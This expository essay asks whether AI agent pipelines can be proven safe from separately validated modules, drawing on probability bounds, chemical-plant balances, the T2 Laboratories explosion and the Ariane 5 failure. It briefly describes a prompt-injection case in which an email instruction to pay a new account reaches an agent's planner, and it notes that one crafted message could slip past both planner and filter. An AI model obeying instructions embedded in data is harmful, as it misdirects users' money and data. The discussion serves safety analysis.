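# Can trustworthy AI agent pipelines be built from separately validated safety modules?

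## The question, and the arithmetic of combining guarantees

An AI agent pipeline is a system in which a language model and other software parts pass work to one another to act on someone's behalf. Suppose an office worker asks an assistant to answer a supplier's email about an unpaid invoice, and to pay the invoice if it matches the contract. A mail reader fetches the message and extracts its text. A retriever finds the contract in the company's files. A planner, usually the language model, compares the two documents and decides what to do. A tool caller submits the payment to the bank. An output filter checks the reply for confidential material before it leaves the company. These five parts are modules because each has stated inputs and outputs, and an engineer can test or replace it separately.

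One proposal based on that structure is to validate each module once, reuse it in any pipeline that needs it, and derive the safety of the whole pipeline from its modules and how they fit together. Chemical engineers design very different plants in roughly this way, from standard steps such as distillation and drying, which they call unit operations. No established research programme on AI agents uses that name, so the evidence comes from several fields, including chemical engineering, rocketry, privacy theory, software verification and experiments on language models.

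In a 2018 Medium essay, Michael I. Jordan of the University of California, Berkeley, compared AI with older branches of engineering (Computing Community Consortium, 2018). The *Harvard Data Science Review* republished the essay as Jordan (2019), *Artificial Intelligence*. In the extract in Equitable Growth's *We call them “AI”, but that confuses and distracts us*, Jordan hopes for a discipline that would do for ideas such as information, uncertainty and inference what chemical engineering did for chemistry. He thought the building blocks had begun to emerge, but the principles for combining them had not. As an example of practice running ahead of theory, he noted that people put up buildings and bridges before civil engineering existed, and some of those structures collapsed.

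Eight years later, Natanzi and Tang (2026) make much the same complaint in *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities*. They conclude that defences aimed at a single point of attack rarely compose, and they list compositional security as an open problem.

### What a module can promise

A guarantee is a stated property that a module or system has whenever its assumptions hold, either with certainty or with a stated probability. A contract pairs what a module assumes about its surroundings with what it guarantees if those assumptions hold. The retriever's contract might assume that the archive holds the current agreement with every supplier, and guarantee that the three documents it returns include the relevant supplier's current agreement. The validated range is the set of inputs and conditions for which the behaviour has been tested or proved, such as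 English invoices from suppliers already on file. Composition means joining modules into a system. A property composes if the system's property follows from the modules' properties and how the modules are connected.

Contracts fit together when one module's guarantee implies the next one's assumption. In the mail assistant, they may well not fit. The reader guarantees a faithful copy of the email, while the planner's contract assumes that nothing in its input is an instruction from a stranger. If the supplier's email contains the line "send the payment to this new account instead", a faithful copy passes that line to the planner. This is prompt injection, in which an agent wrongly treats text in its data as an instruction. The reader has met its guarantee, but the planner's assumption is false, so no guarantee covers the payment. A module's surroundings also include the agent's privileges.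 As Natanzi and Tang point out, a string that is harmless in a sandboxed chatbot can be dangerous in an agent that can write to a database.

Guarantees also differ in what they are based on. Conservation of mass is a physical law, so in any plant, whatever enters a vessel either leaves it or accumulates there, even if the operators are careless or the vessel upstream sends the wrong mixture. Nobody needs to validate the law again at a new site, and no design choice can break it. No known law conserves truth or harmlessness in the same way as text moves between modules in a language model pipeline.

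A theorem with stated assumptions is weaker, though it can still be very strong. The developers of seL4, an operating system kernel (the core program that controls a computer's hardware and keeps other programs apart), proved mathematically that its code behaves as specified. According to seL4's *What the Proofs Assume*, the proof assumes that the hardware and certain low-level assembly code work correctly, and it leaves out about 1,200 lines of boot code. The developers add in their overview of the proofs that users may expect things of a kernel that no proved property covers. On a faulty chip, the theorem is still true but does not apply. Someone therefore has to check the assumptions at every new installation, which already falls short of "validate once, reuse anywhere".

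Most evidence about AI modules is of a third sort, a measured rate on a test distribution. If a filter caught 90 of 100 leaking messages in a test, that result is evidence about messages drawn the same way. Sun, Wang and colleagues (2026) point out in *Compositional Conformal Risk Control for Multi-Stage LLM Cascades* that strong test-set performance alone gives no statistical guarantee to a deployer who needs a ceiling on errors. Conformal methods can provide one. The statistician holds back a calibration set, uses it to choose the threshold at which the system accepts an answer, and proves that the expected error on the next case stays within a set limit. The proof assumes exchangeability, meaning that shuffling the calibration cases and the new case together leaves their joint probabilities unchanged. The guarantee is therefore a theorem, but deployment can violate its assumption. *C-RAG*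 (2024) notes that ordinary conformal guarantees can fail when the data shift, and extends them to retrieval systems whose data shift in limited ways.

Shifts are routine in a pipeline because each module determines the next one's inputs. Joining modules therefore already moves the downstream module's inputs away from its test data, and replacing the planner's language model moves them again. For this reason, *A Three-Layer Probabilistic Assume-Guarantee Architecture Is Structurally Required* (Bensalem, Dong and colleagues, 2026) calls for re-estimating success rates after every change of model. Attackers are a worse problem than drift, because a filter that misses 10% of ordinary leaks may miss every leak phrased in the one way an attacker has found to work.

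### Chains

In a chain, every module must work for the system to be safe. Let pᵢ be the probability that module i works and qᵢ = 1 − pᵢ the probability that it fails. The chain breaks if at least one module fails, and the probability of that cannot exceed the sum of the separate failure probabilities, since the sum counts any occasion on which two modules fail together twice. Mathematicians call this the union bound, or Boole's inequality. Subtracting from one gives

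P(all n modules work) ≥ p₁ + p₂ + … + pₙ − (n − 1).

The bound holds however the failures depend on one another. If five stages each work 99% of the time, all five work together at least 95% of the time (4.95 − 4 = 0.95). If the failures are independent, the figure is 0.99⁵, or 95.1%. It is highest, at 99%, when all five fail on exactly the same occasions. For short chains of good modules, not knowing how the failures are related therefore makes little difference. The number of stages matters more. With 100 stages at 99% each, the bound falls to zero, and even if the failures are independent, all the stages work together only 37% of the time.

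In *TRAQ*, Li, Lee and colleagues (2023) built a question-answering system on this bound. They calibrated the retriever so that its set of passages contains the relevant one with probability at least 1 − α₁. Separately, they calibrated the language model so that, given the relevant passage, its set of answers contains a correct one with probability at least 1 − α₂. The system pools the answers from every retrieved passage, and the pool contains a correct answer with probability at least 1 − (α₁ + α₂). If α₁ and α₂ are both 5%, that probability is at least 90%.

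This is about as close as the proposal comes to working as described, but the guarantee depends on three conditions. Test questions must come from the same distribution as the calibration questions, the relevant passage must be among the retriever's top results (20 in the experiments), and a correct answer must be among the model's samples (30). For each dataset, Li and colleagues collected 1,000 questions that met the last two conditions, so their results confirm the arithmetic when the assumptions hold but don't show how often ordinary questions meet them. The guarantee also applies to a set of candidate answers, not to the single payment the mail assistant has to make.

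Sun and colleagues get an exact sum instead of a bound. In their cascade, a cheap model answers first, and a query moves on to another model only if the first one's confidence is too low. At most one stage accepts each query, so accepted errors at different stages never overlap. To add up correctly, each stage's errors must be measured as a share of all queries, not just the ones it accepts. A stage that accepts 10 of 100 queries and gets two wrong has an error rate of 20%, but contributes 2% to the system's risk. Sun and colleagues certify these contributions by running the whole frozen cascade on held-out queries, so a stage's certificate doesn't apply if the module is used elsewhere. Their headline comparison also sets the total risk budget at 45%, far more than a payment system could tolerate.

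The chain formula has a more serious gap. It bounds the probability that every module works, and using it to bound the safety of the system assumes that the system is safe whenever they all do. Zhang, Liu and colleagues (2026), in *Compositional Safety Failures in Harness Evolution*, tested that assumption on an agent built around the open model Qwen3-32B. The agent's memory, prompts, skills and tools changed with experience. They paired updates to different components, none of them crafted by an attacker, kept only the pairs in which each update was safe and useful alone, and then switched both on. In the banking tasks of AgentDojo, a benchmark for agents, 22 of 157 such pairs (14%) led to a safety violation that had not occurred with either update alone or with neither. On the broader Agent Security Bench, 19 of 1,243 pairs did.

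Their illustration is almost trivial. One update adds Bob to the group that may access stored bank accounts, and another stores a new account. Either change is harmless without the other; together they let Bob into the account. Checking all pairs does not close the gap either, since 15 of 138 eligible triples on AgentDojo went wrong only with all three updates active. The percentages depend heavily on how the experimenters chose the tasks, and "safe alone" means safe in the test runs, so 14% is no estimate for agents in general. It is enough to show that the step can fail in practice, and *Safety is Non-Compositional* (2026) offers a formal proof that it can fail in principle. A complete bound on harm needs one more term:

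P(harm) ≤ q₁ + q₂ + … + qₙ + r,

where r is the probability of harm on occasions when every module meets its own specification. Tests of single modules carry no information about r. Engineers must either prove from the contracts that it is zero or estimate it on the assembled system.

### Barriers

Safeguards that back one another up follow different arithmetic. Here harm occurs only if all of them fail. Suppose three filters check each outgoing reply, and each misses 10% of the messages that leak something. If their misses are independent, all three miss 0.1 × 0.1 × 0.1, or 0.1%, of the leaks. Without independence, the only ceiling that the separate rates supply is the smallest of them:

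P(all n barriers fail) ≤ the smallest of q₁, …, qₙ.

The three filters could together miss 10% of leaks, a hundred times the figure if their errors were independent. If they all miss the same messages, for instance because none of them can read text in a particular encoding, the second and third filters add nothing. The useful rates to measure are how often the second filter misses leaks that the first missed, and how often the third misses leaks that the first two missed. If those rates were 50% and 80%, the three filters would together miss 0.1 × 0.5 × 0.8 = 4% of leaks.

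Dependence thus pushes chains and barriers in opposite directions, and with two modules the reason is visible in one line of algebra. Let c be the covariance of their successes, which is positive when they tend to succeed and fail together. Then

P(both work) = p₁p₂ + c and P(both fail) = q₁q₂ + c.

The same quantity goes into both expressions. In a chain it adds to the probability of safety, and in a pair of barriers it adds to the probability of harm. For two modules that each work 90% of the time:

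| Covariance c | Chain: both work | Barriers: both fail |
|---|---|---|
| −0.01 (failures never coincide) | 80% | 0% |
| 0 (independent) | 81% | 1% |
| 0.05 | 86% | 6% |
| 0.09 (failures always coincide) | 90% | 10% |

A covariance of 0.05 cuts the chain's failure rate by about a quarter, from 19% to 14%, but multiplies the barriers' failure rate by six.

Esary, Proschan and Walkup (1966) proved the general result for any number of components in *A Multivariate Notion of Association, with a Reliability Application*. For two components, non-negative covariance is enough. For more, they needed a stronger condition called association, which requires non-negative covariance between any two quantities that never decrease as components improve. Checking components in pairs is not enough. Three coins rigged so that the number of heads is always even are independent in every pair, yet they never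 all land heads. Huseby and Dahl, in *STK3405*, a course at the University of Oslo, conclude that when components are associated, wrongly assuming independence underestimates the reliability of a chain and overestimates that of parallel back-ups. They add that the direction of the error cannot be predicted for a system that mixes the two arrangements.

The mail assistant contains both a chain and a barrier. For a payment to the wrong account, the planner and the tool caller form a chain, and the output filter can't help because it reads only the reply. For a leak of confidential text, the filter is a barrier behind the planner. If the planner and filter run on the same language model, one cleverly worded email may get past both, and the filter's 90% score on its own test set is then a poor guide to what it will catch.

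## A chemical plant: what balance equations settle and what they leave open

Conservation laws hold in every chemical plant, but they cover only amounts of matter and energy. Judging whether a plant is safe requires further evidence, and a fatal explosion in Florida in 2007 shows what can happen when a company does not collect it.

### From catalogues to equations

Industrial chemists used to study each process, such as making soap or sulphuric acid, separately. Chemical engineers turned to the steps that many processes share, as Willis's 1966 article *Unit Operations to Transport Phenomena* explains. Arthur D. Little, a Boston consultant, named these steps "unit operations" and gave examples including roasting, crystallising, filtering and evaporation. Flavell-While's *Arthur D Little* quotes him as writing that the list of such operations was short, and that engineers could break down any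 process, "on whatever scale conducted", into them. He wrote that chemical engineering was difficult because temperatures and pressures vary between processes and because the chemicals set limits on materials and equipment.

Flavell-While dates the passage to a 1916 speech, but 1915 is the better date for the term. Little used it that year in a report to the president of the Massachusetts Institute of Technology (MIT), according to the Science History Institute's *Arthur D. Little, William H. Walker, and Warren K. Lewis*. Cohen's *The Early History of Chemical Engineering* (1996) also gives 1915. The confusion may come from a training school that Little promoted at the same time. MIT Chemical Engineering's *The History of the Practice School* dates the school's origin to 1915 and its launch to 1916.

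The idea of shared steps was older than the name. George Davis, a consultant in Manchester, lectured on chemical engineering in 1887 and published a handbook in 1901, with chapters on topics such as evaporation and distillation. Purdue University's *Towards the Establishment of a School of Chemical Engineering* points out that the handbook contained no equations. A reader could learn from it which equipment suited which job, but could not calculate how a still would perform in a new plant.

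Walker, Lewis and McAdams supplied the calculations in *Principles of Chemical Engineering* (1923), which Cohen describes as the first textbook to put unit operations in quantitative form. The book drew on years of measurements, in which researchers ran each type of equipment under many conditions and related its performance to feed rate, temperature, pressure and the properties of the fluids. With those data, engineers could often design a unit without first building an expensive pilot plant. Cohen argues that unit operations could not have existed before the 1910s, because nobody had yet done this research. Jordan's complaint that AI has the building blocks before the principles for combining them would also have applied fairly well to chemical engineering in 1901.

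### The general balance

Draw an imaginary boundary around any part of a plant, and choose something to count, such as kilograms of water. Then

accumulation = in − out + production − consumption.

The last two terms are zero for total mass and for each chemical element, because reactions rearrange atoms without creating or destroying them. They usually aren't zero for a single compound, because a reactor turns one compound into another. The atoms still have to balance, so an engineer who knows how much of one compound the reaction consumed can calculate how much of the other it produced.

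Now connect two units. Unit A takes in a feed F and sends a stream S to unit B, which delivers a product P. Their balances are

accumulation in A = F − S + production in A − consumption in A

accumulation in B = S − P + production in B − consumption in B.

When we add the two lines, S cancels:

accumulation in both = F − P + production in both − consumption in both.

The sum has the same form as the balance for one unit, so an engineer can treat the pair as a single unit and attach a third. Balances compose in this strict sense for pumps, stills and reactors alike. Nobody has to check whether A's guarantee implies B's assumption, because whatever leaves A through the pipe enters B. If the pipe leaks, the leak is another outflow, and the measured flows fail to balance by the size of the leak.

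However, because S cancels out, the overall balance for the pair holds whether the stream between the units is a trickle or large enough to wreck unit B.

### A plant with a recycle

In a small example, a reactor receives 100 moles of fresh feed an hour (a mole is a chemist's unit for counting molecules) and converts half of whatever enters it into product. A separator removes the product and returns 90% of the unreacted material to the reactor. The other 10% leaves the plant.

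Let R be the total feed to the reactor. Half of R comes out unreacted, and 90% of that half, or 0.45R, comes back. When the plant runs steadily, nothing accumulates, so

R = 100 + 0.45R, which gives R = 100/(1 − 0.45) = 182 mol/h.

If the conversion falls to 20%, perhaps because the catalyst has aged, 80% of the reactor feed comes out unreacted. The separator then returns 0.72R, and R becomes 100/(1 − 0.72) = 357 mol/h.

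| Flow (mol/h) | Conversion 50% | Conversion 20% |
|---|---|---|
| Fresh feed | 100 | 100 |
| Total reactor feed | 182 | 357 |
| Converted to product | 91 | 71 |
| Returned by the separator | 82 | 257 |
| Leaving the plant unreacted | 9 | 29 |

In both columns, 100 mol/h enters the plant and 100 mol/h leaves it or becomes product. The separator still returns exactly the share it should. Someone who watched only the plant's output would see it drop by about a fifth, but would miss that the flow through the reactor had nearly doubled and the recycle stream had more than tripled.

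If the manufacturer tested the reactor only up to 250 mol/h, it is now far outside its validated range. The engineer can find the limit by setting R to 250 in the balance and solving for the conversion, which gives one third. If conversion drops below that, the reactor will leave its tested range. The engineer can't tell from the balance whether conversion will drop that far, because that depends on the catalyst.

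Testing the catalyst separately may not answer it either. In a well-stirred reactor where the reaction rate is proportional to the concentration of the raw material, the conversion is K/(K + R), where K measures how active the catalyst is. In the original plant K is 182, which gives the conversion of 50%. If the catalyst loses 51% of its activity, K falls to 89. A technician who tests it at the old flow of 182 mol/h will measure a conversion of 33%. If she puts that figure into the balance, she will predict a reactor feed of about 252 mol/h, barely over the limit. But the extra recycle pushes material through the reactor faster, so it has less time to react, more of it comes back, and the flow rises again. The plant settles at a conversion of 20% and a reactor feed of 357 mol/h. Her prediction fails, even though her measurement was accurate and the balance is exact, because the conversion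 depends on the flow, and the flow depends on the rest of the plant.

As another example, suppose the fresh feed contains 1 mol/h of an impurity that never reacts, and the separator returns it along with the raw material. The same formula, with a conversion of zero, gives a reactor feed of 10 mol/h of impurity. With a better separator that returns 99%, the figure rises to 100 mol/h. Improving the separator has made the reactor harder to run, and a single-pass test of the reactor in a rig would not reveal this. Engineers usually limit the buildup by bleeding off part of the recycle stream.

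### Coefficients and scale

Conservation laws are one of three kinds of law that Willis lists as the basis of unit operations. Equilibrium laws describe where a process comes to rest, and rate laws describe how fast it gets there. Rate laws contain coefficients that differ between substances. In Fourier's law, for example, heat flow is proportional to how steeply the temperature changes, and the constant of proportionality is the material's thermal conductivity.

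Fluids can differ greatly in their Prandtl number, which compares how readily a fluid spreads momentum with how readily it spreads heat. Willis gives rough values of 1 for air, 5 for water and 0.01 for mercury. Energy is conserved in all three, but an engineer who fitted a heat-transfer formula to measurements on water would have no grounds for applying it to mercury.

A reactor that gives off heat brings these ingredients together. Its energy balance, in simplified form, is

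C × (rate of temperature rise) = Q(T) − U × A × (T − T꜀).

C is the heat needed to warm the contents by one degree. Q(T) is the heat the reaction releases each minute at temperature T. The last term is the heat passing through a wall of area A to a coolant at temperature T꜀, and U is a coefficient for how easily heat crosses that wall. Conservation of energy fixes only the form of the equation. Chemists have to measure Q, and engineers have to measure U, whose measured value goes out of date as deposits build up on the wall.

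On the right-hand side, the cooling term rises in proportion to the temperature difference, while the heat from most reactions rises much more steeply as the mixture warms. Above some temperature, the reaction therefore heats the vessel faster than the wall can cool it. The extra heat speeds up the reaction, which releases still more heat, a process engineers call a runaway reaction.

Size also matters. If an engineer doubles every dimension of a vessel, it holds eight times as much reacting material but has only four times as much wall, so each square metre of wall has to carry away twice as much heat. Little was right that the same operations appear at every scale, but the numbers that describe them change with size.

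### The explosion at T2 Laboratories

T2 Laboratories, a small company in Jacksonville, Florida, made a petrol additive. According to the U.S. Chemical Safety Board's *T2 Laboratories, Inc. Runaway Reaction* (2009), one of its two owners, a chemist, developed the process by running about 110 test batches in a one-litre reactor, and he never saw extreme heating. The small reactor sometimes needed warming but did not need cooling.

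In January 2004 T2 began production in a 2,450-gallon (about 9,300-litre) vessel. If this vessel had been the same shape as the smaller one, it would have had about one twenty-first as much wall area per litre of mixture through which to lose heat. The first full-scale batch gave off unexpected heat in the first step, and T2 added cooling to that step. The reaction ran out of control in the fifth batch, and the tenth also grew hotter than expected. After the eleventh, one of the owners told investors that the plant had started up successfully. At batch 42 T2 increased the batch size by a third. Investigators found no record of a new process analysis for the change.

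On 19 December 2007, during batch 175, the operator reported a cooling problem. Ten minutes later the reactor burst. The explosion killed four people, injured 32 and released as much energy as 1,400 pounds of TNT.

The investigators concluded that insufficient cooling was the only credible cause, though they could not say which part had failed. A stuck valve, a blocked pipe or mineral deposits in the cooling jacket could each have been enough, because the system had no back-up. Scaling up the process did not cause the explosion by itself, since the plant had already run 174 batches without one, but it made a process that had needed no cooling in the laboratory completely dependent on it.

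The owner's laboratory tests also never went above 380°F (193°C), about six degrees Celsius below the start of the reaction that destroyed the plant. When the U.S. Chemical Safety Board had the recipe tested, a second reaction, between the sodium in the mixture and the solvent, appeared above 390°F (199°C). It raised the temperature by about 1,300°C a minute and burst the test cells.

The reactor did have a safeguard, a rupture disc designed to burst and release pressure. The other owner, a chemical engineer, had sized it for the hydrogen given off in normal operation, and employees said it was set to burst at 400 pounds per square inch. Once the second reaction had begun, a disc with that setting would probably not have saved the vessel, whatever its size. A disc set to burst at 75 would probably have released the pressure during the first reaction, early enough to prevent the second.

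T2's production record could not have shown that the process was safe. At most 133 batches at the larger size came before the last one. Even if all of them had gone perfectly and had been independent trials under identical conditions, they would have ruled out, at 95% confidence, only failure rates above about 2.2% per batch. At the three batches a week that T2 was making by the end, that rate would mean more than three failures a year.

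### Why safety has no balance equation

Federal safety rules did not cover the danger either. The workplace regulator's process safety standard applied to a list of hazardous chemicals and to large quantities of flammable liquid. T2 used none of the listed chemicals, and its first-step mixture did not meet the legal definition of a flammable liquid. The U.S. Chemical Safety Board had earlier studied 167 serious accidents involving chemical reactions in the United States between 1980 and mid-2001, and found that more than half involved chemicals outside the existing federal process safety rules.

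A list of ingredients is a poor guide to danger because much of the danger comes from how the ingredients react with each other. Sodium and the solvent were in the same vessel in batch after batch, but they reacted violently only above a certain temperature. Mixing can also remove danger. Hydrochloric acid and caustic soda both burn skin, but in the right proportions they react to form salt water.

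A balance equation for danger would be useless. It would set the amount leaving a plant equal to the amount entering plus the amount produced inside, but no independent rule fixes the production term, so an engineer could always pick a value afterwards that made the equation hold. The balance for mass rules out some outcomes because its production term is zero, and the balance for a compound does so because the atoms have to add up.

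### Searching the connected plant for deviations

Chemical engineers cannot calculate safety from a balance, so they search for ways the plant could go wrong. The best-known method is the hazard and operability study, or HAZOP. A team that includes designers and operators goes through the drawings of the connected plant one section at a time. For each section, the team combines quantities such as flow, temperature and pressure with guide words such as "no", "more", "less" and "reverse" to identify possible deviations, such as "no flow" in a cooling line. The team then asks what could cause each deviation, what would follow, and whether the existing safeguards would be adequate.

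One of T2's design consultants recommended a HAZOP, but the U.S. Chemical Safety Board found no evidence that the company ever carried one out. Part of the worksheet might have looked like this:

| Deviation | Possible cause | What the team would need to find out |
|---|---|---|
| No cooling water | Supply valve fails closed, or drain valve sticks open | How hot the mixture gets, and what reacts above 380°F |
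| More pressure | Reaction makes gas faster than in normal operation | Whether the rupture disc can release it in time |
| More reactants | Company increases the batch size | Whether the jacket and the disc are still adequate |

None of the entries in the last column requires the team to know about the second reaction in advance. The first row leads to an experiment that would have revealed it. The investigators similarly thought that a thorough HAZOP would probably have shown that T2 needed to test how the reaction behaved and how much its cooling and pressure relief could handle.

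The method also suits the recycle plant. One cause of "more flow" at the reactor inlet is downstream: the separator sends back unreacted material. A specification for the reactor alone would list a maximum flow but could not list the reasons a particular plant might exceed it.

A HAZOP can't give the kind of guarantee a balance gives, because it depends on the team's knowledge and patience. It also tends to take deviations one at a time, so the team can miss an accident that needs two at once. It helps engineers find accidents that can happen even when every module meets its specification (the term r in the bound on harm), but it produces a list of scenarios rather than a probability, so it doesn't put a number on r. For the worst scenarios, engineers add further safeguards and give separate credit only to those that don't share a cause of failure, which are called independent protection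 layers.

### Plants built from ready-made modules

Some chemical companies now buy parts of their plants as finished modules, which comes closer to the proposal for AI agents. *Modularization in Chemical Processing* (2018), from the American Institute of Chemical Engineers, describes factory-built blocks that workers connect on site. A block may contain one unit operation, several, or only part of one. For a typical refinery project, modular construction can cut the total cost by about 30%, and extensive use of modules can shorten a three-year project to two. The assembled plant does exactly what a conventional plant would do, so the savings come from where and how people build it, and the hazards of the process remain.

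Modules offer one way round the problem of scale. A company can install many copies of a small reactor instead of building a larger one, which engineers call numbering up. Each copy stays at the size that was tested. For some equipment this is the only safe choice. AIChE notes that the channels in a microchannel reactor can be no more than a few millimetres high, because the gas might burn in taller ones. The validated range for such equipment includes size as well as temperature. But numbering up has practical limits. T2 would have needed more than 9,000 of its laboratory reactors to match its production vessel.

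Copies also share services. In the modular designs that AIChE describes, one main pipe supplies the modules with the compressed air that operates their instruments. A loss of air could therefore disturb several modules at once, however well each performed in its own tests. At T2, one of the faults that could have stopped the cooling was a failure of the air system that moved the water valves.

Connecting the controls is the easier part of the job. The Module Type Package, a standard that began in German industry, is a file that a manufacturer supplies with a module. It describes the module's functions and signals in a common format, so that control systems from different suppliers can start, stop and monitor the module. A correct file shows that the control system can operate the module, but not that the module is safe next to a particular neighbour. For instance, a pump module that can deliver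 10 bar might sit directly upstream of a filter module built to withstand only 6 bar, even if both modules have correct files and have passed every test their makers set.

The safety work therefore has two parts. The manufacturer can study once what might go wrong inside the module and give every buyer that analysis, along with the limits on pressure, temperature and flow. The company that assembles the plant has to compare those limits with what the neighbouring modules can deliver, including when they malfunction, and then look for hazards that exist only in the connected plant, such as recycle loops, shared services and chemicals that must be kept apart. Reuse greatly reduces the work in the first part, but the second has to be redone for each new arrangement, though a good description of every module makes it quicker.

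AI developers could copy this division of labour, and it would be an improvement on testing modules alone, but they would still have nothing like the cancellation of S. Some quantities do add up across an agent pipeline, such as running time and the cost of calls to a language model, but they have little to do with harm. To serve the purpose that mass serves in a chemical plant, a quantity would need a value that engineers can establish for each module separately, and a rule for combining those values that holds however the modules are connected. It would also need a known limit on how much of it any module can create, and a proven link to some harm that people want to prevent.

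## Ariane 5: a validated module reused outside its range

An engineer can compare a module's limits with what other modules send it only if someone has written those limits down. Nobody had done this for a navigation unit that the European rocket Ariane 5 reused from Ariane 4. Ariane 5 broke up on its first flight, on 4 June 1996. *Ariane 5 Flight 501 Failure* (1996), the Inquiry Board's report, traces the loss to the conversion of a single number.

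### The loss of flight 501

The unit, called an inertial reference system, uses gyroscopes and accelerometers to work out which way the rocket is pointing and how it is moving. It sends the results to the main computer, which steers by swivelling the engine nozzles. Ariane 5 carried two of these units with identical hardware and software, one active and one on standby. Their design was practically the same as on Ariane 4.

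Part of the software aligned the unit while the rocket stood on the launch pad. It served no purpose after lift-off, but it kept running for about 40 seconds of flight. Ariane's engineers had asked for this more than ten years earlier so that they could restart a countdown stopped in its last seconds without a normal alignment, which took 45 minutes or more. They used the feature once, in 1989. Ariane 5 had a different countdown and did not need it, but the project kept it so that the two rockets would have the same software.

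The flight was normal for 36 seconds after the command to ignite the main engine. The failure then unfolded as follows:

1. Ariane 5's horizontal velocity built up five times as fast as Ariane 4's. The alignment software calculated a quantity called horizontal bias, which depends on that velocity, and it grew unusually large.
2. The software converted the bias from a 64-bit floating-point number to a 16-bit signed integer, which can hold only whole numbers from −32,768 to 32,767. At 36.7 seconds the bias no longer fitted, and the conversion caused an error.
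3. The unit's specification required the processor to shut down after any such error, so the standby unit stopped.
4. The active unit, running the same software on the same motion, stopped about 0.05 seconds later.
5. The active unit then sent diagnostic data to the main computer, which processed them as flight data. The computer swung the nozzles as far as they would go, to correct a deviation that had not occurred.
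6. The rocket turned more than 20 degrees away from the airflow. The air tore the boosters from the main stage, which triggered the self-destruct system.

The alignment software would have switched itself off about ten seconds after the error. Shutting down a faulty processor helps when the fault is a random hardware failure, because an identical backup can take over, but not when both processors share a design error.

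The programmers had considered this kind of error and found seven variables that might not fit their number format. They protected four but left three unprotected, including the horizontal bias, to keep the processor's workload below a target of 80%. They reasoned that the three were either physically limited or had a large margin of safety, but the Ariane 5 Inquiry Board found no evidence that anyone had checked this against trajectory data. Ariane 4 never exceeded the limit. But if the bias grew in proportion to horizontal velocity, a value that took up only a quarter of the available range on Ariane 4 would have overflowed on Ariane 5.

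### The tests that nobody ran

The supplier tested the unit rigorously under environmental conditions beyond those expected on Ariane 5, but nobody tested it with Ariane 5's countdown and trajectory. The project partners had agreed to leave the trajectory out of the unit's requirements, so the supplier had no reason to include it when testing against them. Engineers could have run the test on the ground by feeding simulated accelerometer signals into the unit while a turntable reproduced the rocket's rotation. The Ariane 5 Inquiry Board concluded that this would have exposed the fault.

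Simulations of the whole flight gave the project another chance to find the overflow. The original plan included the real units, but in 1992 the engineers decided to replace them with software models, partly because the units were already fully qualified on their own. They also argued that the test signals would not be precise enough, and that they could simulate equipment failures only with a model. They then ran many complete simulated flights, and the overflow never appeared.

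The investigators accepted these arguments as technically valid, but they saw a definite risk in treating the unit as validated because it had passed its own tests or had worked on Ariane 4. When engineers later ran the unit's software on the actual trajectory of flight 501, it failed as it had in flight.

### The missing contract

The inertial unit had no written contract pairing its assumptions (A) with its guarantees (G). The investigators wanted something similar for every mission-critical device, which they called a "declaration of limitation". For the inertial unit, a contract might have looked like this:

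| Part of the contract | Content |
|---|---|
| Assumption about the flight | While the alignment software is running, the horizontal bias stays between −32,768 and 32,767 |
| Assumption about faults | Faults are random hardware failures, so the two units do not stop together |
| Guarantee in normal operation | The unit sends attitude and velocity data of a stated accuracy in every cycle |
| Guarantee after a failure | The unit sends a signal that the main computer cannot mistake for flight data |

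The supplier would have to state the limit in the first entry as a maximum horizontal velocity for each second of flight, because the rocket's designers know the trajectory but not the unit's internal variables.

To join two modules with contracts (A₁, G₁) and (A₂, G₂), an engineer has to show that each guarantee establishes the other's assumption, with the help of whatever is known about the surroundings, E:

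E and G₁ together imply A₂

E and G₂ together imply A₁.

Flight 501 broke this rule in both directions. The main computer was keeping the rocket on Ariane 5's trajectory, as it was meant to, when the units failed, but that trajectory violated the units' first assumption. The computer's software, in turn, relied on receiving flight data, but the failed unit sent diagnostics instead.

*Contracts for System Design* (Benveniste et al., 2018) also gives a rule for replacing modules. A new module can safely replace an old one if it assumes no more about its surroundings and guarantees at least as much. Ariane's engineers instead kept the module and changed its surroundings. That is safe only if the new surroundings satisfy the module's old assumptions, and successful flights on Ariane 4 are no evidence that they do.

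### Modules that depend on each other

On a rocket, these modules form a loop. The unit measures the motion, the computer uses the measurements to steer, and the steering changes the motion that the unit measures next. The unit works only if the computer keeps the rocket within limits, which the computer can do only if the unit works. Using each guarantee to prove the other therefore looks circular.

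Sometimes it is. Suppose a buyer promises to pay eventually if the seller eventually delivers, and the seller promises to deliver eventually if the buyer eventually pays. Both can do nothing forever without breaking their promises.

Martín Abadi and Leslie Lamport, in *Composing Specifications* (1993), and *Conjoining Specifications* (1995), worked out when such reasoning is sound. The main condition is that the assumptions are safety properties. In this technical sense, a safety property states that something bad never happens, so any violation occurs at a definite moment. A promise to pay "eventually" is different, because there is no moment at which the buyer has broken it. In its simplest form, the argument also needs each module to keep its guarantee for one step longer than its assumption has held. It then runs by induction:

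- Both guarantees hold at the start.
- If both hold up to step n, then both assumptions hold up to step n, so both guarantees hold up to step n + 1.

The argument is that neither module can be the first to fail, so neither fails. Ariane's guidance loop fits the form of this argument because the computer steers by measurements from a moment earlier. The argument still fails for flight 501, because even a rocket exactly on course violated the unit's assumption.

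Benveniste and colleagues handle circularity by writing each guarantee as a conditional, "if the assumption holds, then the guarantee holds". They calculate the weakest condition on the surroundings under which each conditional establishes the other module's assumption. For the buyer and seller, the condition is that at least payment or delivery takes place. The promises alone don't ensure this, so whoever joins the modules has to arrange it.

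An AI agent also contains a loop, since its planner reads the results of its earlier tool calls. "No confidential text has left the company" is a safety property, so the inductive argument can apply in principle. Engineers would still have to show that the planner keeps its guarantee at each step, and for a language model they have usually only measured how often it does. Bensalem and colleagues therefore attach probabilities to their contracts.

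### How the car industry permits reuse

Car makers buy microcontrollers and operating systems from suppliers who often do not know which car will contain them. ISO 26262, the international standard for functional safety in road vehicles, allows for this by letting suppliers develop a part as a "safety element out of context". The supplier assumes a set of safety requirements and conditions of use, develops the part to meet them, and delivers the assumptions with the part. The company that integrates the part must confirm that each assumption is true in its car. If one is false, somebody has to change the car or the part and redo the safety work that the change affects.

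Under this procedure, Ariane 5's engineers would have had to compare a velocity limit with their planned trajectory, which they could have done without knowing the unit's code. The procedure depends on the supplier recognising the assumption and stating it prominently. Ariane's partners had agreed to leave the horizontal bias unprotected, but the volume of documentation effectively hid that decision from outside reviewers.

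Machine learning fits the procedure less well. *An Analysis of ISO 26262* (2017) found that the standard did not address the particular features of learned software. It recommended widening the definition of "hazard", because such software can create dangers without any component malfunctioning. It also recommended setting different requirements depending on whether anyone can specify the function. ISO has since published separate guidance on AI in road vehicles, ISO/PAS 8800 (2024).

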